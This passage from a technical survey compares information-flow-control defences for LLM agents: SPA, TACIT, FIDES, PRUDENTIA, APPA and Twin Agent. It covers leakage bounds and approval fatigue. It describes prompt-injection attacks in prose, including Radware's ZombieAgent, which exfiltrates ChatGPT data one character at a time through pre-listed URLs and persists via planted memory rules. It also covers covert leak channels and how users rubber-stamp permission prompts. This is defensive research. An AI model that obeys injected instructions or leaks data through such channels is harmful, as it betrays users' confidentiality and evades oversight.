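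Denning's remedy for skipped lines requires the program text, which an agent has if it fixes its plan in advance. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) checks the whole plan before any tool runs, including what depends on each branch. Its planner writes in a small language designed for such checks and gets only one attempt, so errors cannot carry information back to it. The check reduced successful attacks on AgentDojo to zero, but it reduced completed tasks from 53% to 29%, mainly because the system rejected plans that passed untrusted results to sensitive tools.

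SPA also handles data saved in one request and used in a later one. For example, a user might ask the agent on Monday to save the details of an invoice that contains an attacker's account number, then ask it on Tuesday to pay the invoice. SPA stores the details with their labels and shows Tuesday's planner only a description of the stored data, so the account number is still labeled untrusted when the payment tool runs.

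### The theorem in the LLMbda calculus

The LLMbda calculus, a small language by Garby and colleagues, avoids the gap by stopping the run if a program tries to change anything labelled public inside a branch that depends on a secret. In one test, the program first told the model to remember that x was false. If a secret was true, the program then told the model to set x to true. Its last step was to ask for x. The interpreter stopped the run at the second message because the conversation was still labelled public.

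Stopping can itself reveal something, since the run would have finished if the secret had been false. But it ends the program, so the program cannot go on to leak the next digit. The theorem makes this precise. Take an observer and two starting states that differ only in data the observer may not see. Let μ₁(*o*) and μ₂(*o*) be the probabilities that the run finishes and the observer sees *o*. The probabilities in each case may add up to less than 1, because some runs stop early or never end. The theorem says that there is always a single function ω with

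μ₁(*o*) ≤ ω(*o*) and μ₂(*o*) ≤ ω(*o*) for every *o*, and Σ ω(*o*) ≤ 1.

A program that prints the secret fails this condition. It prints "yes" with probability 1 for one secret and "no" with probability 1 for the other, so ω would have to total at least 2. A program that stops when the secret is true and otherwise prints "done" satisfies the condition, because ω can give "done" a probability of 1.

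If both runs always finish, the condition forces μ₁ and μ₂ to be equal, so the observer learns nothing. Otherwise, the difference between them is at most the average probability of not finishing:

½ Σ |μ₁(*o*) − μ₂(*o*)| ≤ ½ (stop₁ + stop₂).

For the "done" program, both sides equal ½. So the guarantee weakens as more runs stop, and a system that restarted a stopped program could leak a little information with each restart.

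The proof checker Lean has verified the theorem, which holds for any model, even one that an attacker controls completely. It does depend on several other assumptions:

- The developer has labelled the sources correctly and put a check at every sink.
- Each reply is a random draw that depends only on the conversation so far. A service that secretly carried information from one conversation to another would break this.
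- All the data is inside the program. The proof does not model outside tools that change or that others can watch during a run.
- The observer sees the result and not how long it took.

A program may also endorse an untrusted value, which gives up the integrity guarantee for that value. A second theorem shows that endorsement cannot weaken the protection of secrets.

Garby and colleagues wrote an agent called Randori in the language to test whether anyone could work under these rules. Its planner first practises on invented data, where payments do nothing and files contain placeholder text, so errors during practice reveal nothing about the real data. The planner then writes a final program, which runs once. The planner may endorse particular values, but it must decide to do so before it sees any real data.

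With GPT-5.2, Randori completed 36 of the 48 banking runs, twice as many as CaMeL with its checks on. Across three models, two of 1,296 attacks succeeded. In both, the user had asked the agent to pay whatever a file said, and the attacker had replaced the file. When the planner could not endorse anything, completion fell from 75% to 62.5% with one model and from 65% to 54% with another.

This comparison somewhat favors Randori, because Randori enforces only some of CaMeL's policies, in less strict versions. The test covers 16 tasks in one setting, with margins of error around 20 percentage points. Much of the gain probably comes from letting the planner decide in advance that the user trusts a particular file, which CaMeL could also allow. The theorem does not depend on these results.

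### Rejecting the program before it runs

Odersky and colleagues use an existing programming language to rule out leaks before a program starts. Their system, TACIT, requires the agent to write its actions in Scala 3, whose compiler checks the type of every value and can reject a program that breaks the rules. In TACIT, a capability is an object that gives a program permission to do something, such as write to a particular file, whereas in CaMeL it is a tag on data. An experimental compiler feature records in each function's type which capabilities the function uses.

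TACIT wraps confidential text in a type called `Classified`. Agent code can work on the contents only by passing a function to the wrapper's `map` method, and the compiler accepts only functions that use no capabilities:

```
val salary = readClassified("salary.txt")
salary.map(text => text.length)         // accepted
salary.map(text => report.write(text))  // rejected
```

The result of the accepted line is also classified. The compiler rejects the last line because the function uses `report`, a file the program can write to. A function passed to `map` also cannot change a variable outside itself, so the salary-copying program above would not compile. If the agent prints a classified value, the user sees the real text, but the agent's model receives only asterisks. When a task requires understanding the text, the agent can send it to a separate trusted model, whose answer is also classified.

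This protection does not depend on the user's request being honest. Odersky and colleagues tested two models on a software project with a folder of secrets, using 120 combinations of an ordinary task and an injection, plus 11 malicious requests in which the user asked for the secrets directly or impersonated someone with authority. With the secrets wrapped, neither model's output contained any of them. Without the wrapper, MiniMax M2.5 revealed them in response to 8 of the 11 malicious requests and Claude Sonnet 4.6 in response to 2. The wrapper did not reduce the share of ordinary tasks that either model completed.

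Writing Scala also did little harm to general performance. On a benchmark of simulated customer service, three models did slightly better with TACIT than with ordinary tool calls, perhaps because the compiler's error messages helped them. On a set of real software problems, MiniMax M2.5 solved 41.7% with TACIT and 43.3% without it.

Unlike CaMeL's planner, TACIT's agent can read untrusted text and change its plan in response. An injection can therefore redirect the agent, but only to actions that the agent's capabilities permit. On AgentDojo, TACIT blocked every attack except one, in which the agent quoted hotel reviews that contained the attacker's recommendation. Despite this freedom to replan, TACIT did not complete more tasks overall. With o4-mini, CaMeL completed more tasks than TACIT in all four settings, leading by nearly 30 percentage points on office tasks. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, TACIT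 was far ahead on travel tasks, where CaMeL failed almost completely.

The compiler protects only data that someone has marked as classified, and it cannot check what outside programs do once the agent starts them. Odersky and colleagues also leave timing out of their guarantee. Agent code could run longer when a classified number is large, and an outside observer could infer the number from the delay.

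## Fixed answer formats: counting the bits a call can pass on

FIDES and CaMeL give the output of a quarantined call the combined label of everything the call read. A one-word answer to "Does this email ask for a meeting?" gets the same label as a summary of the whole mailbox, although one word can hold far less information. A system can limit what an answer reveals by fixing the possible answers in advance. If a call can return only *N* distinct answers, its answer reveals at most log₂ *N* bits about what the call read, even if an injection fully controls the model.

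### Where the limit comes from

Quantitative information flow is the branch of security theory that measures how much a program leaks. Smith, in *On the Foundations of Quantitative Information Flow* (2009), considers an attacker who sees a program's output and then gets one guess at the secret. Write *X* for the secret and *Y* for the output. Smith defines these quantities:

- **Vulnerability**, V(X) = max P(X = x), is the attacker's chance of guessing the secret before seeing any output. The best guess is the most likely value.
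- **Conditional vulnerability**, V(X|Y) = Σ P(Y = y) · max P(X = x | Y = y), is the average chance of guessing the secret after seeing the output.
- **Min-entropy**, log₂ 1/V, expresses either chance in bits.
- **Leakage** is the min-entropy before the output minus the min-entropy after it, which equals log₂ (V(X|Y) / V(X)).

Suppose the secret is a four-digit PIN and all 10,000 values are equally likely. The attacker's chance of guessing it in one try is 1 in 10,000, which is about 13.3 bits of min-entropy. A truthful answer to "Is the PIN above 4999?" leaves 5,000 possible values and raises the chance to 1 in 5,000, so it leaks one bit.

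No yes/no answer can do better on average. Bayes' theorem turns the conditional vulnerability into

V(X|Y) = Σ max P(Y = y | X = x) · P(X = x),

with one term for each possible output *y*. The first factor is a probability, so it is at most 1, and the second is at most V(X). With *N* outputs, the sum is therefore at most *N* · V(X), and the leakage is at most log₂ *N*.

The proof does not depend on how the program works, so it covers a language model that picks its words partly at random. It also holds for any distribution of secrets. *Quantifying information flow in interactive systems* (Mestel, 2019) shows that the limit extends to a secret that is only related to the input, such as a password that someone could infer from an email. *An Operational Approach to Information Leakage* (Issa, Wagner and Kamath, 2018) proves a similar result for an attacker who wants only some fact about the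 secret, or who gets several guesses.

Smith chose this measure because Claude Shannon's more familiar one, the average number of bits leaked, can make a dangerous program look safe. For example, suppose a program prints a random 128-bit key whenever the key is divisible by 8, and otherwise prints 1. Shannon's measure gives a leak of about 16 bits, but the attacker learns the entire key one time in eight. Smith's measure gives about 125 bits.

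If the answer is the only untrusted input the planner reads, the same count also limits how an attacker can steer the agent, because the planner's next prompt can take only *N* forms. This limits the number of possible outcomes but not the harm in each. If the question is whether to pay an invoice, an attacker who controls the one-bit answer can get a fraudulent invoice paid.

### Enforcing the format

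Asking a model to answer only "yes" or "no" is not enough, since an injection can ask for something else. Constrained decoding uses ordinary software to enforce the format. At each step, the model gives every possible next token (a word or part of a word) a probability, and the software rules out the tokens that would break the format before one is chosen. An injection can still change a "no" to a "yes", but it cannot make the model write an email address.

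The count holds only if the program fixes the list of answers before the call reads the data and discards any reasoning the model writes before its answer. A visible failure counts as one more answer, so a yes/no call that sometimes returns an error can pass log₂ 3, or about 1.6 bits.

In FIDES, the planner specifies the answer format, and the answer's type becomes part of its label. Costa and colleagues rank the types by how much information they can carry, from yes/no to a choice from a fixed list to free text. A policy can then relax the ordinary rules for types that carry little. For example, it may let a yes/no answer from an untrusted web page influence a sensitive action, which amounts to endorsing one bit. A similar policy could declassify a yes/no answer about a confidential file.

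However, the types do not track how many bits several answers carry in total. Joining two yes/no labels gives another yes/no label, although two answers can carry two bits. A policy that accepts any yes/no answer would therefore accept a hundred of them about the same file.

### Agents that pass on only numbers and choices

Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues built and tested agents around this idea in *Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation* (2025). A quarantined model reads the untrusted text and may send the planner only whole numbers, decimal numbers, yes/no values, choices from a list the developer has vetted, or short lists of such values. None of these can express a new instruction, so the planner cannot receive an injected command.

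Their three agents show how much of a task survives:

- **Shopping.** The quarantined model turns each product review into two scores from 0 to 10, one for how strongly the review supports the product and one for its relevance. The planner sees the median scores and the number of reviews, so one hostile review among many has little effect.
- **Scheduling.** The quarantined model turns the other person's emails into a list of one-hour slots. The planner compares the slots with the user's calendar and either proposes new times or books the meeting.
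- **Bug fixing.** The quarantined model reads a bug report and returns the kind of bug and a list of suspicious code regions. Each region consists of a file number, a role, and a first and last line. Another model, which never sees the report, writes three repair plans, and a judge that has seen the report returns only the number of the best one.

| Agent | Model | Tasks completed, undefended | Tasks completed, restricted | Successful attacks, undefended | Successful attacks, restricted |
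|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Shopping | GPT-4o | 21.8% | 22.4% | 31.7% | 0% |
| Scheduling | GPT-4o | 90.0% | 91.0% | 63.0% | 0% |
| Bug fixing | GPT-5.2 | 68.3% | 45.0% | 98.9% | 0% |

The restriction caused no measurable loss in performance where numbers and time slots could express what the planner needed. Bug reports are harder to fit into a fixed format, and the bug-fixing agent completed about a third fewer tasks. Designing its format also took considerable trial and error on a separate set of bugs. An attacker can still mislead the agent with false information, for example by reporting a bug in the wrong file. Jacob and colleagues treat this as a separate problem from prompt injection.

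These types keep out instructions but can still let secrets through. A whole number with no upper limit can encode any secret, and 39 digits are enough for a 128-bit key. Even the bug-fixing format could carry that key in four regions. In a repository of 1,000 files with 1,000 lines each, a region with one of eight roles can take 8 billion values, or about 33 bits. The scheduling test counted an attack as successful only if a marker phrase from the calendar appeared in an email, so it would not have detected a secret encoded in the choice of times, such as the revenue figure that Bob obtained as a meeting date.

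### Short hints in free text

The same research group at Berkeley later tried to recover the lost tasks by allowing a little free text. In *Twin Agent* (Hu, Jacob and colleagues, 2026), an Explore Agent reads everything but cannot act. At each step, it may send a hint of at most 100 or 200 characters, depending on the benchmark, to a Safe Agent, which acts but cannot read untrusted text. The Explore Agent can see what the Safe Agent has done so far, so the hint needs to contain only what is missing for the next step.

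On 232 bug-fixing tasks with planted attacks, GPT-5.2 completed 61.2% without a defence and 62.5% with Twin Agent, while the attack success rate fell from 97% to zero. A version that allowed no communication between the two agents completed no tasks. On AgentDojo, Twin Agent completed 62.9% of tasks with Gemini 2.5 Flash, against 61.9% for the undefended agent and 30.9% for CaMeL, which Hu and colleagues ran with fewer retries than usual. But completion on the Slack tasks fell from 90.5% to 66.7%.

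The security argument is empirical, and Hu and colleagues offer no formal guarantee. They observed that injections now have to be long to fool the strongest models, and they add a detector that screens each hint. When they attacked the design with knowledge of how it works, they could always force the Explore Agent to copy out a hint of their choosing, and in 11 of the 232 tasks (4.7%) the Safe Agent eventually carried out the malicious action. None of the 11 attacks succeeded again in five reruns each, so the successes seem to have been partly luck, but an attacker can also try repeatedly. When they varied the limit on hint length between 50 and 200 characters, longer hints brought more completed tasks and more successful attacks.

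As a limit on leaks, 100 characters is very generous. With 95 printable characters to choose from, one hint can carry 100 × log₂ 95, or about 657 bits. The following table puts the formats side by side:

| Format of one answer | Possible answers | Limit in bits | Answers needed for a 128-bit key |
|---|---|---|---|
| Yes or no | 2 | 1 | 128 |
| Day of the month | 31 | 5.0 | 26 |
| One-hour slot in the scheduling test | 63 | 6.0 | 22 |
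| Two review scores | 121 | 6.9 | 19 |
| One code region, as above | 8 billion | 33 | 4 |
| Hint of 100 characters | 95¹⁰⁰ | 657 | 1 |
| Summary of 300 tokens | 100,000³⁰⁰ | about 4,980 | 1 |

The last row assumes a vocabulary of 100,000 tokens, which gives 300 × log₂ 100,000 bits, enough to hold the key 38 times. The limit is still correct for the summary, but it is too high to rule out any leak an attacker would want. An honest summary of a sales report reveals far less about a key elsewhere in the prompt than the limit allows, but counting possible answers cannot show that. Geometric Information Flow, covered in a later section, tries to estimate how much information actually flowed.

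### ZombieAgent: one character at a time

Narrow channels are safe only if an attacker cannot use them repeatedly. *ZombieAgent*, a disclosure by the security company Radware, describes an attack on ChatGPT that used a narrow channel repeatedly. Earlier attacks had made ChatGPT append stolen data to a web address. OpenAI responded by allowing ChatGPT to open an address only exactly as someone had provided it.

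The attacker's email therefore listed a separate address for each letter, each digit and the space. It told ChatGPT to find something sensitive, convert it to lower case and open the matching addresses in order. Radware's example, the name "Zvika Doe", takes nine visits. This did not break the rule because ChatGPT never altered an address.

There are 37 addresses in the set, so each visit passes up to log₂ 37, or about 5.2 bits. A 128-bit key written as 32 hexadecimal digits needs 32 visits. Radware added numbered versions of each address, such as a0 to a9 for the letter "a", to mark each character's position. The attacker can then reassemble the text even if the requests arrive out of order, so scrambling them would not have helped.

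Radware also made the theft continue across conversations. A shared file placed rules in ChatGPT's memory, and from then on ChatGPT read the attacker's email and followed the instructions in it before answering each message. Radware reported the flaws on 26 September 2025, and OpenAI fixed them on 16 December.

### Leak budgets

A natural response is to add up the bits and stop at a limit. If each of *k* calls has *N* possible answers, there are at most *N*ᵏ sequences of answers, so the calls leak at most *k* · log₂ *N* bits. This holds even if the attacker chooses each question after seeing the previous answer, because the count covers every sequence that a fixed strategy can produce. Mestel shows that the worst case is always some fixed strategy.

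Whether repeated questions come near the limit depends on the questions. Smith compares two that each leak one bit when asked once. "Is the key equal to *g*?" eliminates one value each time, so 128 such questions have only 129 possible outcomes and leak about 7 bits. "Is the key at most *g*?" can halve the possibilities each time, so 128 of these reveal a whole 128-bit key. Mestel proves that the leak from a deterministic system with finitely many states always grows in one of these two ways, either with the logarithm of the running time or in proportion to it. He also gives an efficient test for which one applies. The theorem does not cover systems with random behaviour, such as a model that samples its words.

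An agent's bit budget has to assume that an attacker can choose which question gets answered. The planner may ask a harmless question about an email, but an injection can tell the quarantined model to answer a different one, such as whether the seventeenth bit of a key is 1. The program receives only a "yes", which doesn't show which question was answered.

A budget that counts the worst case for each call usually runs out long before that much information has leaked. *Quantifying Information Leak Vulnerabilities* (2010) calculates that checking a guess against a random 64-bit password leaks about 3.5 × 10⁻¹⁸ bits on average, but the worst case for a yes/no check is still one bit. Refined limits only partly close this gap. In an example in *On the Compositionality of Quantitative Information Flow* (2016), ten channels together leaked 0.13 bits, while the refined limit was 0.74. An assistant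 that sorts incoming email into eight categories can leak up to 3 bits per email, so a 20-bit budget would stop it after six emails, although its answers probably reveal almost nothing.

The right budget size also depends on the secret. After a 20-bit leak, an attacker still has only one chance in 2¹⁰⁸ of guessing a random 128-bit key. The same leak could reveal an entire six-digit login code, which contains just under 20 bits. Whether a company plans to buy a competitor takes only one bit to reveal. Budgets therefore protect keys and passwords much better than business facts, which are often what an office assistant has to protect.

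*Answer-Only Disclosure* (2026) tests a budget in a related setting, where a small local model reads private documents and a cloud model helps to write the answer without seeing them. A ledger counts what each answer discloses against the budget, in nats (one nat is about 1.44 bits). Without a budget, the system revealed a planted code with a million possible values in 46 of 48 attempts. With a budget of 4 or 16 nats per answer, the main version never revealed it. At 4 nats, the paper's theoretical limit on the probability of disclosure was 0.34. At 16 nats there was no guarantee, because the code contains only 13.8 nats. The median answer used 10 nats and a third of answers used more than 16, so the budgets that gave a guarantee would have constrained most ordinary answers.

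The computer-use agents based on FIDES had a cruder budget, which limited how often each variable could be reused. If the limit is five uses and each use returns yes or no, the agent learns at most 5 bits about the variable. Any such counter has to persist across conversations, because otherwise an attack like ZombieAgent's could continue in a new chat with the count reset.

### Signals outside the answer

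The calculation counts only the answers a call can return. An outsider may also see other things, and the budget must include each as an additional channel.

A request whose wording never changes can still pass one bit by being sent or not, so a budget that counts only the requests sent would underestimate how much can leak.

The order of an agent's calls can carry more information than their contents. If an agent has to open ten permitted pages and a compromised model chooses the order, there are 10! (3,628,800) possible orders, enough to pass almost 22 bits. The log would list the same ten pages every time, so a reviewer would have to compare the sequences to notice a difference.

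Timing is not limited to a fixed number of values. An attacker who can distinguish 60 delays, each one second apart, gets up to 5.9 bits from each delay, nearly six times what a yes/no answer passes. Issa and colleagues cite an attack on SSH, a protocol for logging in to remote computers, in which the attacker used the gaps between keystrokes to reduce the search for a password by a factor of at least 250, or about 8 bits, without decrypting anything.

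A program can close these channels by making the same calls in the same order at fixed times, whatever the answers are. This requires unnecessary page loads and delays, and the agent can no longer adapt its actions to what it finds. A less drastic step is to measure what leaves the network, as *Silent Egress* (2026) does. It found that agents could leak sensitive data through tool calls while their written answers showed no sign of it, so measuring only the answers would miss these leaks.

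## The cost of labelling everything: lost tasks, approvals and spreading labels

When a label check refuses a tool call, the program can ask the user to approve it, so conservative labelling can leave tasks unfinished, take up employees' attention, or both. The AgentDojo tests of FIDES and CaMeL measured only task completion. Of two experiments from 2026, one also counts approvals, and the other simulates how far labels spread when several agents share the work.

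### Counting approvals

Kolluri and colleagues note that companies' agents without information-flow control (IFC) usually stop for approval before every consequential action. GitHub Copilot Chat in Visual Studio Code, for example, runs read-only tools without asking and requests approval for the rest. An agent with IFC needs approval only for calls that violate its policy.

For a run τ, let *v*(τ) be the number of calls that need approval. Over *n* tasks, the two measures are

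approval load = Σ *v*(τᵢ), summed over the completed tasks,

TCR@*k* = (number of tasks completed with *v*(τᵢ) ≤ *k*) / *n*,

where TCR stands for task completion rate. TCR@0 is the share of tasks the agent finishes without asking anyone, and TCR@∞ is the share it finishes if a person approves everything. The load leaves out failed tasks because the agent mostly spent them repeating refused calls, and a person would have stopped it.

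Earlier papers had reported that deterministic defences reduce task completion on AgentDojo by up to 30%. Kolluri and colleagues argue that this comparison was unfair, because it gave the protected agent no approvals and let the undefended agent act as if someone had approved everything. With OpenAI's o4-mini, FIDES completes 53.2% of tasks without approvals and the undefended agent completes 70.1% with unlimited approvals, an apparent loss of 17 points. FIDES is ahead when both agents work under the same rules, by 53.2% to 32.8% without approvals and by 75.7% to 70.1% with unlimited approvals.

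The argument works for a company that would otherwise make its staff approve every consequential action, but many users don't work that way. According to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), a quarter of interactive Claude Code sessions started in a mode that bypasses permission prompts. The older comparison is closer to what those users would notice, although the agent they are used to doesn't have the protection of permission prompts.

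### A planner that knows the policy

PRUDENTIA keeps the enforcement code of FIDES but gives its planner more information. The FIDES planner cannot see the policies, so it may open a variable and then be unable to act. In PRUDENTIA, each tool's description includes the policy that governs it, and the planner can see the label of its own context. Before opening a variable, the planner has to call a `plan` tool, give a reason for opening it, and list the calls it intends to make next.

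The agent can then open the variable after asking the user to endorse the data, which keeps the context trusted, or without asking, which makes the context untrusted. Kolluri and colleagues give the example of an email with a to-do list of ten items, each of which requires a consequential action. An agent that reads the email without endorsement needs ten approvals. If the user endorses the email, the agent needs only that one interaction.

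Asking users to endorse data interrupts them needlessly when no consequential action follows. In one AgentDojo task, the user asks for a day's appointments and a password reset link. PRUDENTIA opened the calendar entries and the email without asking, since it only had to report what they said. The search for the link had also returned a message from an aol.com address with a similar name. The agent used the other message, but the policy would not have blocked the wrong choice because it does not check text shown to the user.

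PRUDENTIA has no equivalent for confidentiality. Whether a private document may go to someone depends on the situation, so Kolluri and colleagues left out general declassification, and the user approves each call that would send one.

They compared four planners on AgentDojo without attacks, running each experiment five times. "Basic" asks about every consequential call. "Basic with IFC" plans in the same way but asks only when a check fails. The approval loads were:

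| Planner | GPT-4o | o3-mini | o4-mini | GPT-5 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Basic | 59.4 | 48.2 | 48.6 | 52.0 |
| Basic with IFC | 39.4 | 32.4 | 34.6 | 40.4 |
| FIDES | 7.8 | 18.8 | 36.8 | 41.3 |
| PRUDENTIA | 23.8 | 16.4 | 19.2 | 7.3 |

The next table gives the percentage of tasks completed with no approvals, followed by the percentage with unlimited approvals:

| Planner | GPT-4o | o3-mini | o4-mini | GPT-5 |
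|---|---|---|---|---|
| Basic | 28.0 / 72.2 | 24.3 / 62.5 | 32.8 / 70.1 | 35.1 / 72.3 |
| Basic with IFC | 38.4 / 72.2 | 35.5 / 62.5 | 42.5 / 70.1 | 43.4 / 72.3 |
| FIDES | 50.3 / 56.3 | 50.1 / 64.3 | 53.2 / 75.7 | 57.1 / 78.9 |
| PRUDENTIA | 42.5 / 61.4 | 59.1 / 69.8 | 59.4 / 73.2 | 72.7 / 80.0 |

With o3-mini, adding labels and checks to the basic agent reduced the approval load by a factor of 1.5 and left task completion unchanged. PRUDENTIA needed 1.9 times fewer approvals than FIDES with o4-mini and more than five times fewer with GPT-5. With GPT-4o, however, it needed three times as many approvals as FIDES and completed fewer tasks without approval. Planning around a policy apparently takes a fairly capable model. Completing more of the hard tasks also raises the approval load, so it makes sense to read the two tables together.

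PRUDENTIA's planning uses a lot of text, so it cost 4.7 cents per task on Slack tasks with GPT-4o, compared with 2.2 cents for FIDES and 0.5 cents for the basic agent with IFC. Kolluri and colleagues had not tried to reduce this cost, and it is small compared with the cost of interrupting an employee.

PRUDENTIA was also tested on WASP, a benchmark with simulated GitLab and Reddit sites. In each of its 84 test cases, the agent has to comment on a post or upvote it while the site contains instructions planted in an issue or post. PRUDENTIA hid all text written by users in variables and left buttons and text boxes visible. It needed no approvals, and no attack diverted it. The basic agent averaged between 1.0 and 3.7 approvals per task, depending on the model and site, and attacks diverted it in 15% to 61% of cases. However, WASP contains only data-independent tasks, such as upvoting a post,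 which doesn't require reading it, so a planner can do all of them without opening a variable.

### What an approval is worth

In these counts, Kolluri and colleagues treat an approval as safe. They assume that a person would stop any dangerous call that reached them, though they mention the risk that people stop reading the prompts, known as approval fatigue.

Anthropic found that users approve 97% of Claude Code's permission prompts. To learn how carefully people read them, it paid for a study in which 1,053 professional testers did coding work and, at some point in each session, saw a clearly dangerous command in place of the real one. The testers refused it 13.6% of the time, and the rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts. They may have been less careful because the code was not their own. Anthropic also published the result to justify replacing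 the prompts with an automatic classifier, which blocked 89% of the same commands. Even if the true refusal rate is several times higher, human approval is a weak last check.

The pattern also appears outside Anthropic's data. In *Habituation at the Gate*, Yu, Jia and colleagues (2026) followed 400 people who repeatedly reviewed code changes written by AI agents. The reviewers approved 27.9% of changes in the first tenth of their reviews and 42.4% in the last tenth, while their comments per review fell by 22%. Approval of human-written changes in the same projects fell over the period. The agents' code may have improved, which would justify some of the rise in approvals. It probably would not justify the drop in comments among the reviewers whose approvals rose most.

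Some users turn off approval prompts. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) analysed 290 reports about agents' handling of files and found that user review was a factor in 105. In 80 of these, the user had set the agent to approve everything, in some cases to avoid hundreds of prompts per session. In 31, the prompt gave too little information. For instance, approving `python3 setup.py` authorises whatever the script contains. Software practitioners interviewed for *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026) described clicking through familiar prompts and skipping review when short of time.

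Letting people write standing rules may not help much. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (2026), participants who wrote such rules saw fewer prompts about actions that went beyond their request, but approved more of them. Users had approved 133 of the 148 such actions that went ahead.

Asking for one endorsement instead of ten approvals should make users read more carefully. Claude Code users reject 39% of the plans it presents and 3% of single permission requests, though they may reject a plan because it is bad rather than unsafe. But an endorsement covers everything in the email. If an attacker has added an eleventh item in white text, one click makes it trusted and the agent carries it out without asking. With separate approvals, the agent would at least have asked the user about the eleventh action.

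### Dividing the work between agents

A company could also reduce approvals by giving each agent a smaller job, so that a strict label stays with the agent that picked it up. Gregory and colleagues tested how much this helps in a November 2026 simulation that runs no language model. Each task is a random graph of tool calls, where an arrow from one call to another means that the later call needs the earlier one's output. With *m* calls, each possible arrow appears with probability 2/(*m* + 1), giving slightly under one arrow per call on average. The simulation assigns every call to an agent at random and marks some calls as sensitive.

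An agent becomes sensitive for the rest of the task if it runs a sensitive call, or if it receives or relays information from an agent that is already sensitive. The measure of damage is

loss = (calls that introduce a sensitive label or run under one) / (all calls).

Gregory and colleagues compared a mesh, in which every agent can contact every other, with a ring, a star, a hierarchy and five random networks. Their baseline contains exactly the links a given task needs. The arrangement affects how far labels spread because agents that relay messages pick up labels too. Suppose a finance agent sends a salary total to a reporting agent. In a mesh, only those two agents get the salary label. In a star, the total goes through the hub, so every later message through the hub also gets the label, including a room booking for the calendar agent.

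With five agents and tasks of 20 calls, four of them sensitive, the star lost about 5 percentage points more than the baseline, the hierarchy about 4 and the ring about 3. The mesh matched the baseline. Across the nine fixed arrangements, loss fell almost consistently as the share of possible links that existed rose (rank correlation −0.96).

Increasing the number of agents from 5 to 20 also reduced the loss, because each agent's context then held less. But it adds channels to watch. A mesh of *n* agents has *n*(*n* − 1)/2 links, so the number rises from 10 to 190. Gregory and colleagues suggest that a random network with about 30% of those links can come close to the mesh's performance. Grouping the sensitive calls on particular agents, such as one that handles all banking, reduced the loss in every arrangement. The baseline gained the most, so the star and the other sparse arrangements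 fell further behind it.

The loss figure is the share of calls that a policy might refuse. The simulation contains no policy, and it counts a sensitive call as lost even if the agent was entitled to make it and nobody stopped it. If 10 of the 20 calls are sensitive, the loss is at least 50% however the company arranges its agents. The simulation also has no planner that could reorder its work to avoid a label, as PRUDENTIA does, and no office documents to show how often tasks mix sensitive and ordinary steps. It can rank arrangements, but it cannot predict how many of a company's tasks would fail. Gregory and colleagues leave real workloads to later work.

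### APPA: reading in a branch

Someone must decide in advance how to divide work among permanent agents. *APPA* instead lets an ordinary agent create a temporary agent when it needs one. The program stops before a read that would make the agent's label stricter and offers a choice between accepting the stricter label and having a temporary agent do the read.

A branch is a copy of the agent that starts with the same conversation and the same label. The branch reads the document, and only the branch takes on the stricter label. Before the branch starts, the parent fixes the form of its answer, which may contain yes/no values, numbers within set limits and choices from a list, but no free text. The program checks the answer's form, passes the answer to the parent and discards the rest of the branch. If the branch goes wrong, the parent can abandon it and keep its own label unchanged, but this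 doesn't undo anything the branch did in the outside world.

One of the paper's test tasks asks the assistant to confirm that Alice Chen's record is on file with HR, log a ticket, and send a routine update to the whole company. An agent with a single context label can no longer write to everyone once it has read the record. If a branch reads the record instead, the parent only needs to learn that the record exists. As with other fixed answer formats, someone still has to decide in advance that this answer may be public, and an injection can still make the answer false.

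*APPA* proves that reading more data can never clear a message that has failed the check on its recipients or on trust, since reading only tightens the label. The program lists what could clear it. A person, a fixed rule or another model can rule on that one call, or a trusted program can produce a cleaned version of the data, for example with personal details removed. A ruling applies only to that exact call and does not change the label. A hidden eleventh item on the to-do list would therefore need its own ruling, but so would each of the ten real items if they all failed the check.

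*APPA* also checks the label that a call would produce, as well as the current one. Otherwise, a tool that reads a confidential ledger and emails it in a single step would pass the check, because the context is still clean when the call begins.

On Bench-Corp, a set of 20 office scenarios, *APPA* reports 87–91% of tasks completed across three models and no successful attacks in 600 runs. Two configurations of Microsoft's FIDES implementation completed 36–46% of tasks, and attacks succeeded in 26–35% of runs. This is weak evidence against FIDES, because the scenarios were built to exercise *APPA*'s mechanisms and some involve rules that the FIDES policies could not express, such as sending an announcement only once. On AgentThreatBench, an existing set of 24 tasks, *APPA* completed 64–77% with no successful attacks, and FIDES sometimes completed more.

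A more useful test removed parts of *APPA*. With GPT-5.6 Luna, the full system completed 88% of the Bench-Corp runs, compared with 56.5% without branches and 35% without the listed remedies. The attack rate was zero in all three versions, so branches and remedies let the system complete more runs without weakening the checks in the tested scenarios.

### SPA: labels that last between requests

A branch lasts only as long as its task, but an office assistant also has to remember information between tasks. SPA stores results with their labels and shows its planner only descriptions of the results. To measure how much this hurts performance, Girrens and Wang split each of AgentDojo's 97 tasks into two to five successive requests, so that later requests depend on the results of earlier ones. They used a small model, GPT-5.4-nano.

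| Measure | Without label checks | With label checks |
|---|---|---|
| Tasks completed, single request | 53.0% | 29.0% |
| Tasks completed, several requests | 62.5% | 35.3% |
| Successful attacks, single request | 0.4% | 0% |
| Successful attacks, several requests | 0.3% | 0.2% |
| Available stored results that later plans retrieved | 95.4% | 89.9% |

Hiding stored text from the planner had little effect on task completion. With label checks off, Girrens and Wang found that showing the planner the actual contents raised completion by only 3.4 points. The label checks lowered completion by 24 to 27 points. In the single-request tests they stopped only four successful attacks out of 949, because fixing the plan in advance had already blocked the others. That benefit looks small for the number of tasks lost, but the attack used in the tests barely covers delayed attacks through stored data,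 which SPA is also meant to stop. Two of the successful attacks recorded with the checks on were also runs in which SPA had rejected the plan.

SPA rejected about 53% of the single-request plans. It applies one trust requirement to all of a tool's arguments, so it can reject an email whose text draws on a web page just as it can reject one whose recipient comes from the page. FIDES can require trust for the recipient alone. Girrens and Wang suggest separate requirements for each argument and limited endorsement. SPA never asks for approval, so its results correspond to TCR@0.

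### Why a real mailbox may be harder

Most of these figures come from AgentDojo or tasks derived from it, and AgentDojo probably understates how much labels hinder agents. *AgentDyn* (Li, Wen and colleagues, 2026) reports that only 6 of AgentDojo's 97 tasks require the agent to revise its plan after seeing data, a narrower category than the data-dependent tasks in the FIDES tests. Its own 60 tasks all require replanning and average 7.1 steps across about three applications, against 3.5 steps in one or two applications for AgentDojo. Each task also includes a useful third-party instruction, such as a checkout page that asks the user to log in first. None of the defences it compared performed acceptably, and those that depend on an initial plan, including CaMeL, completed far fewer tasks.

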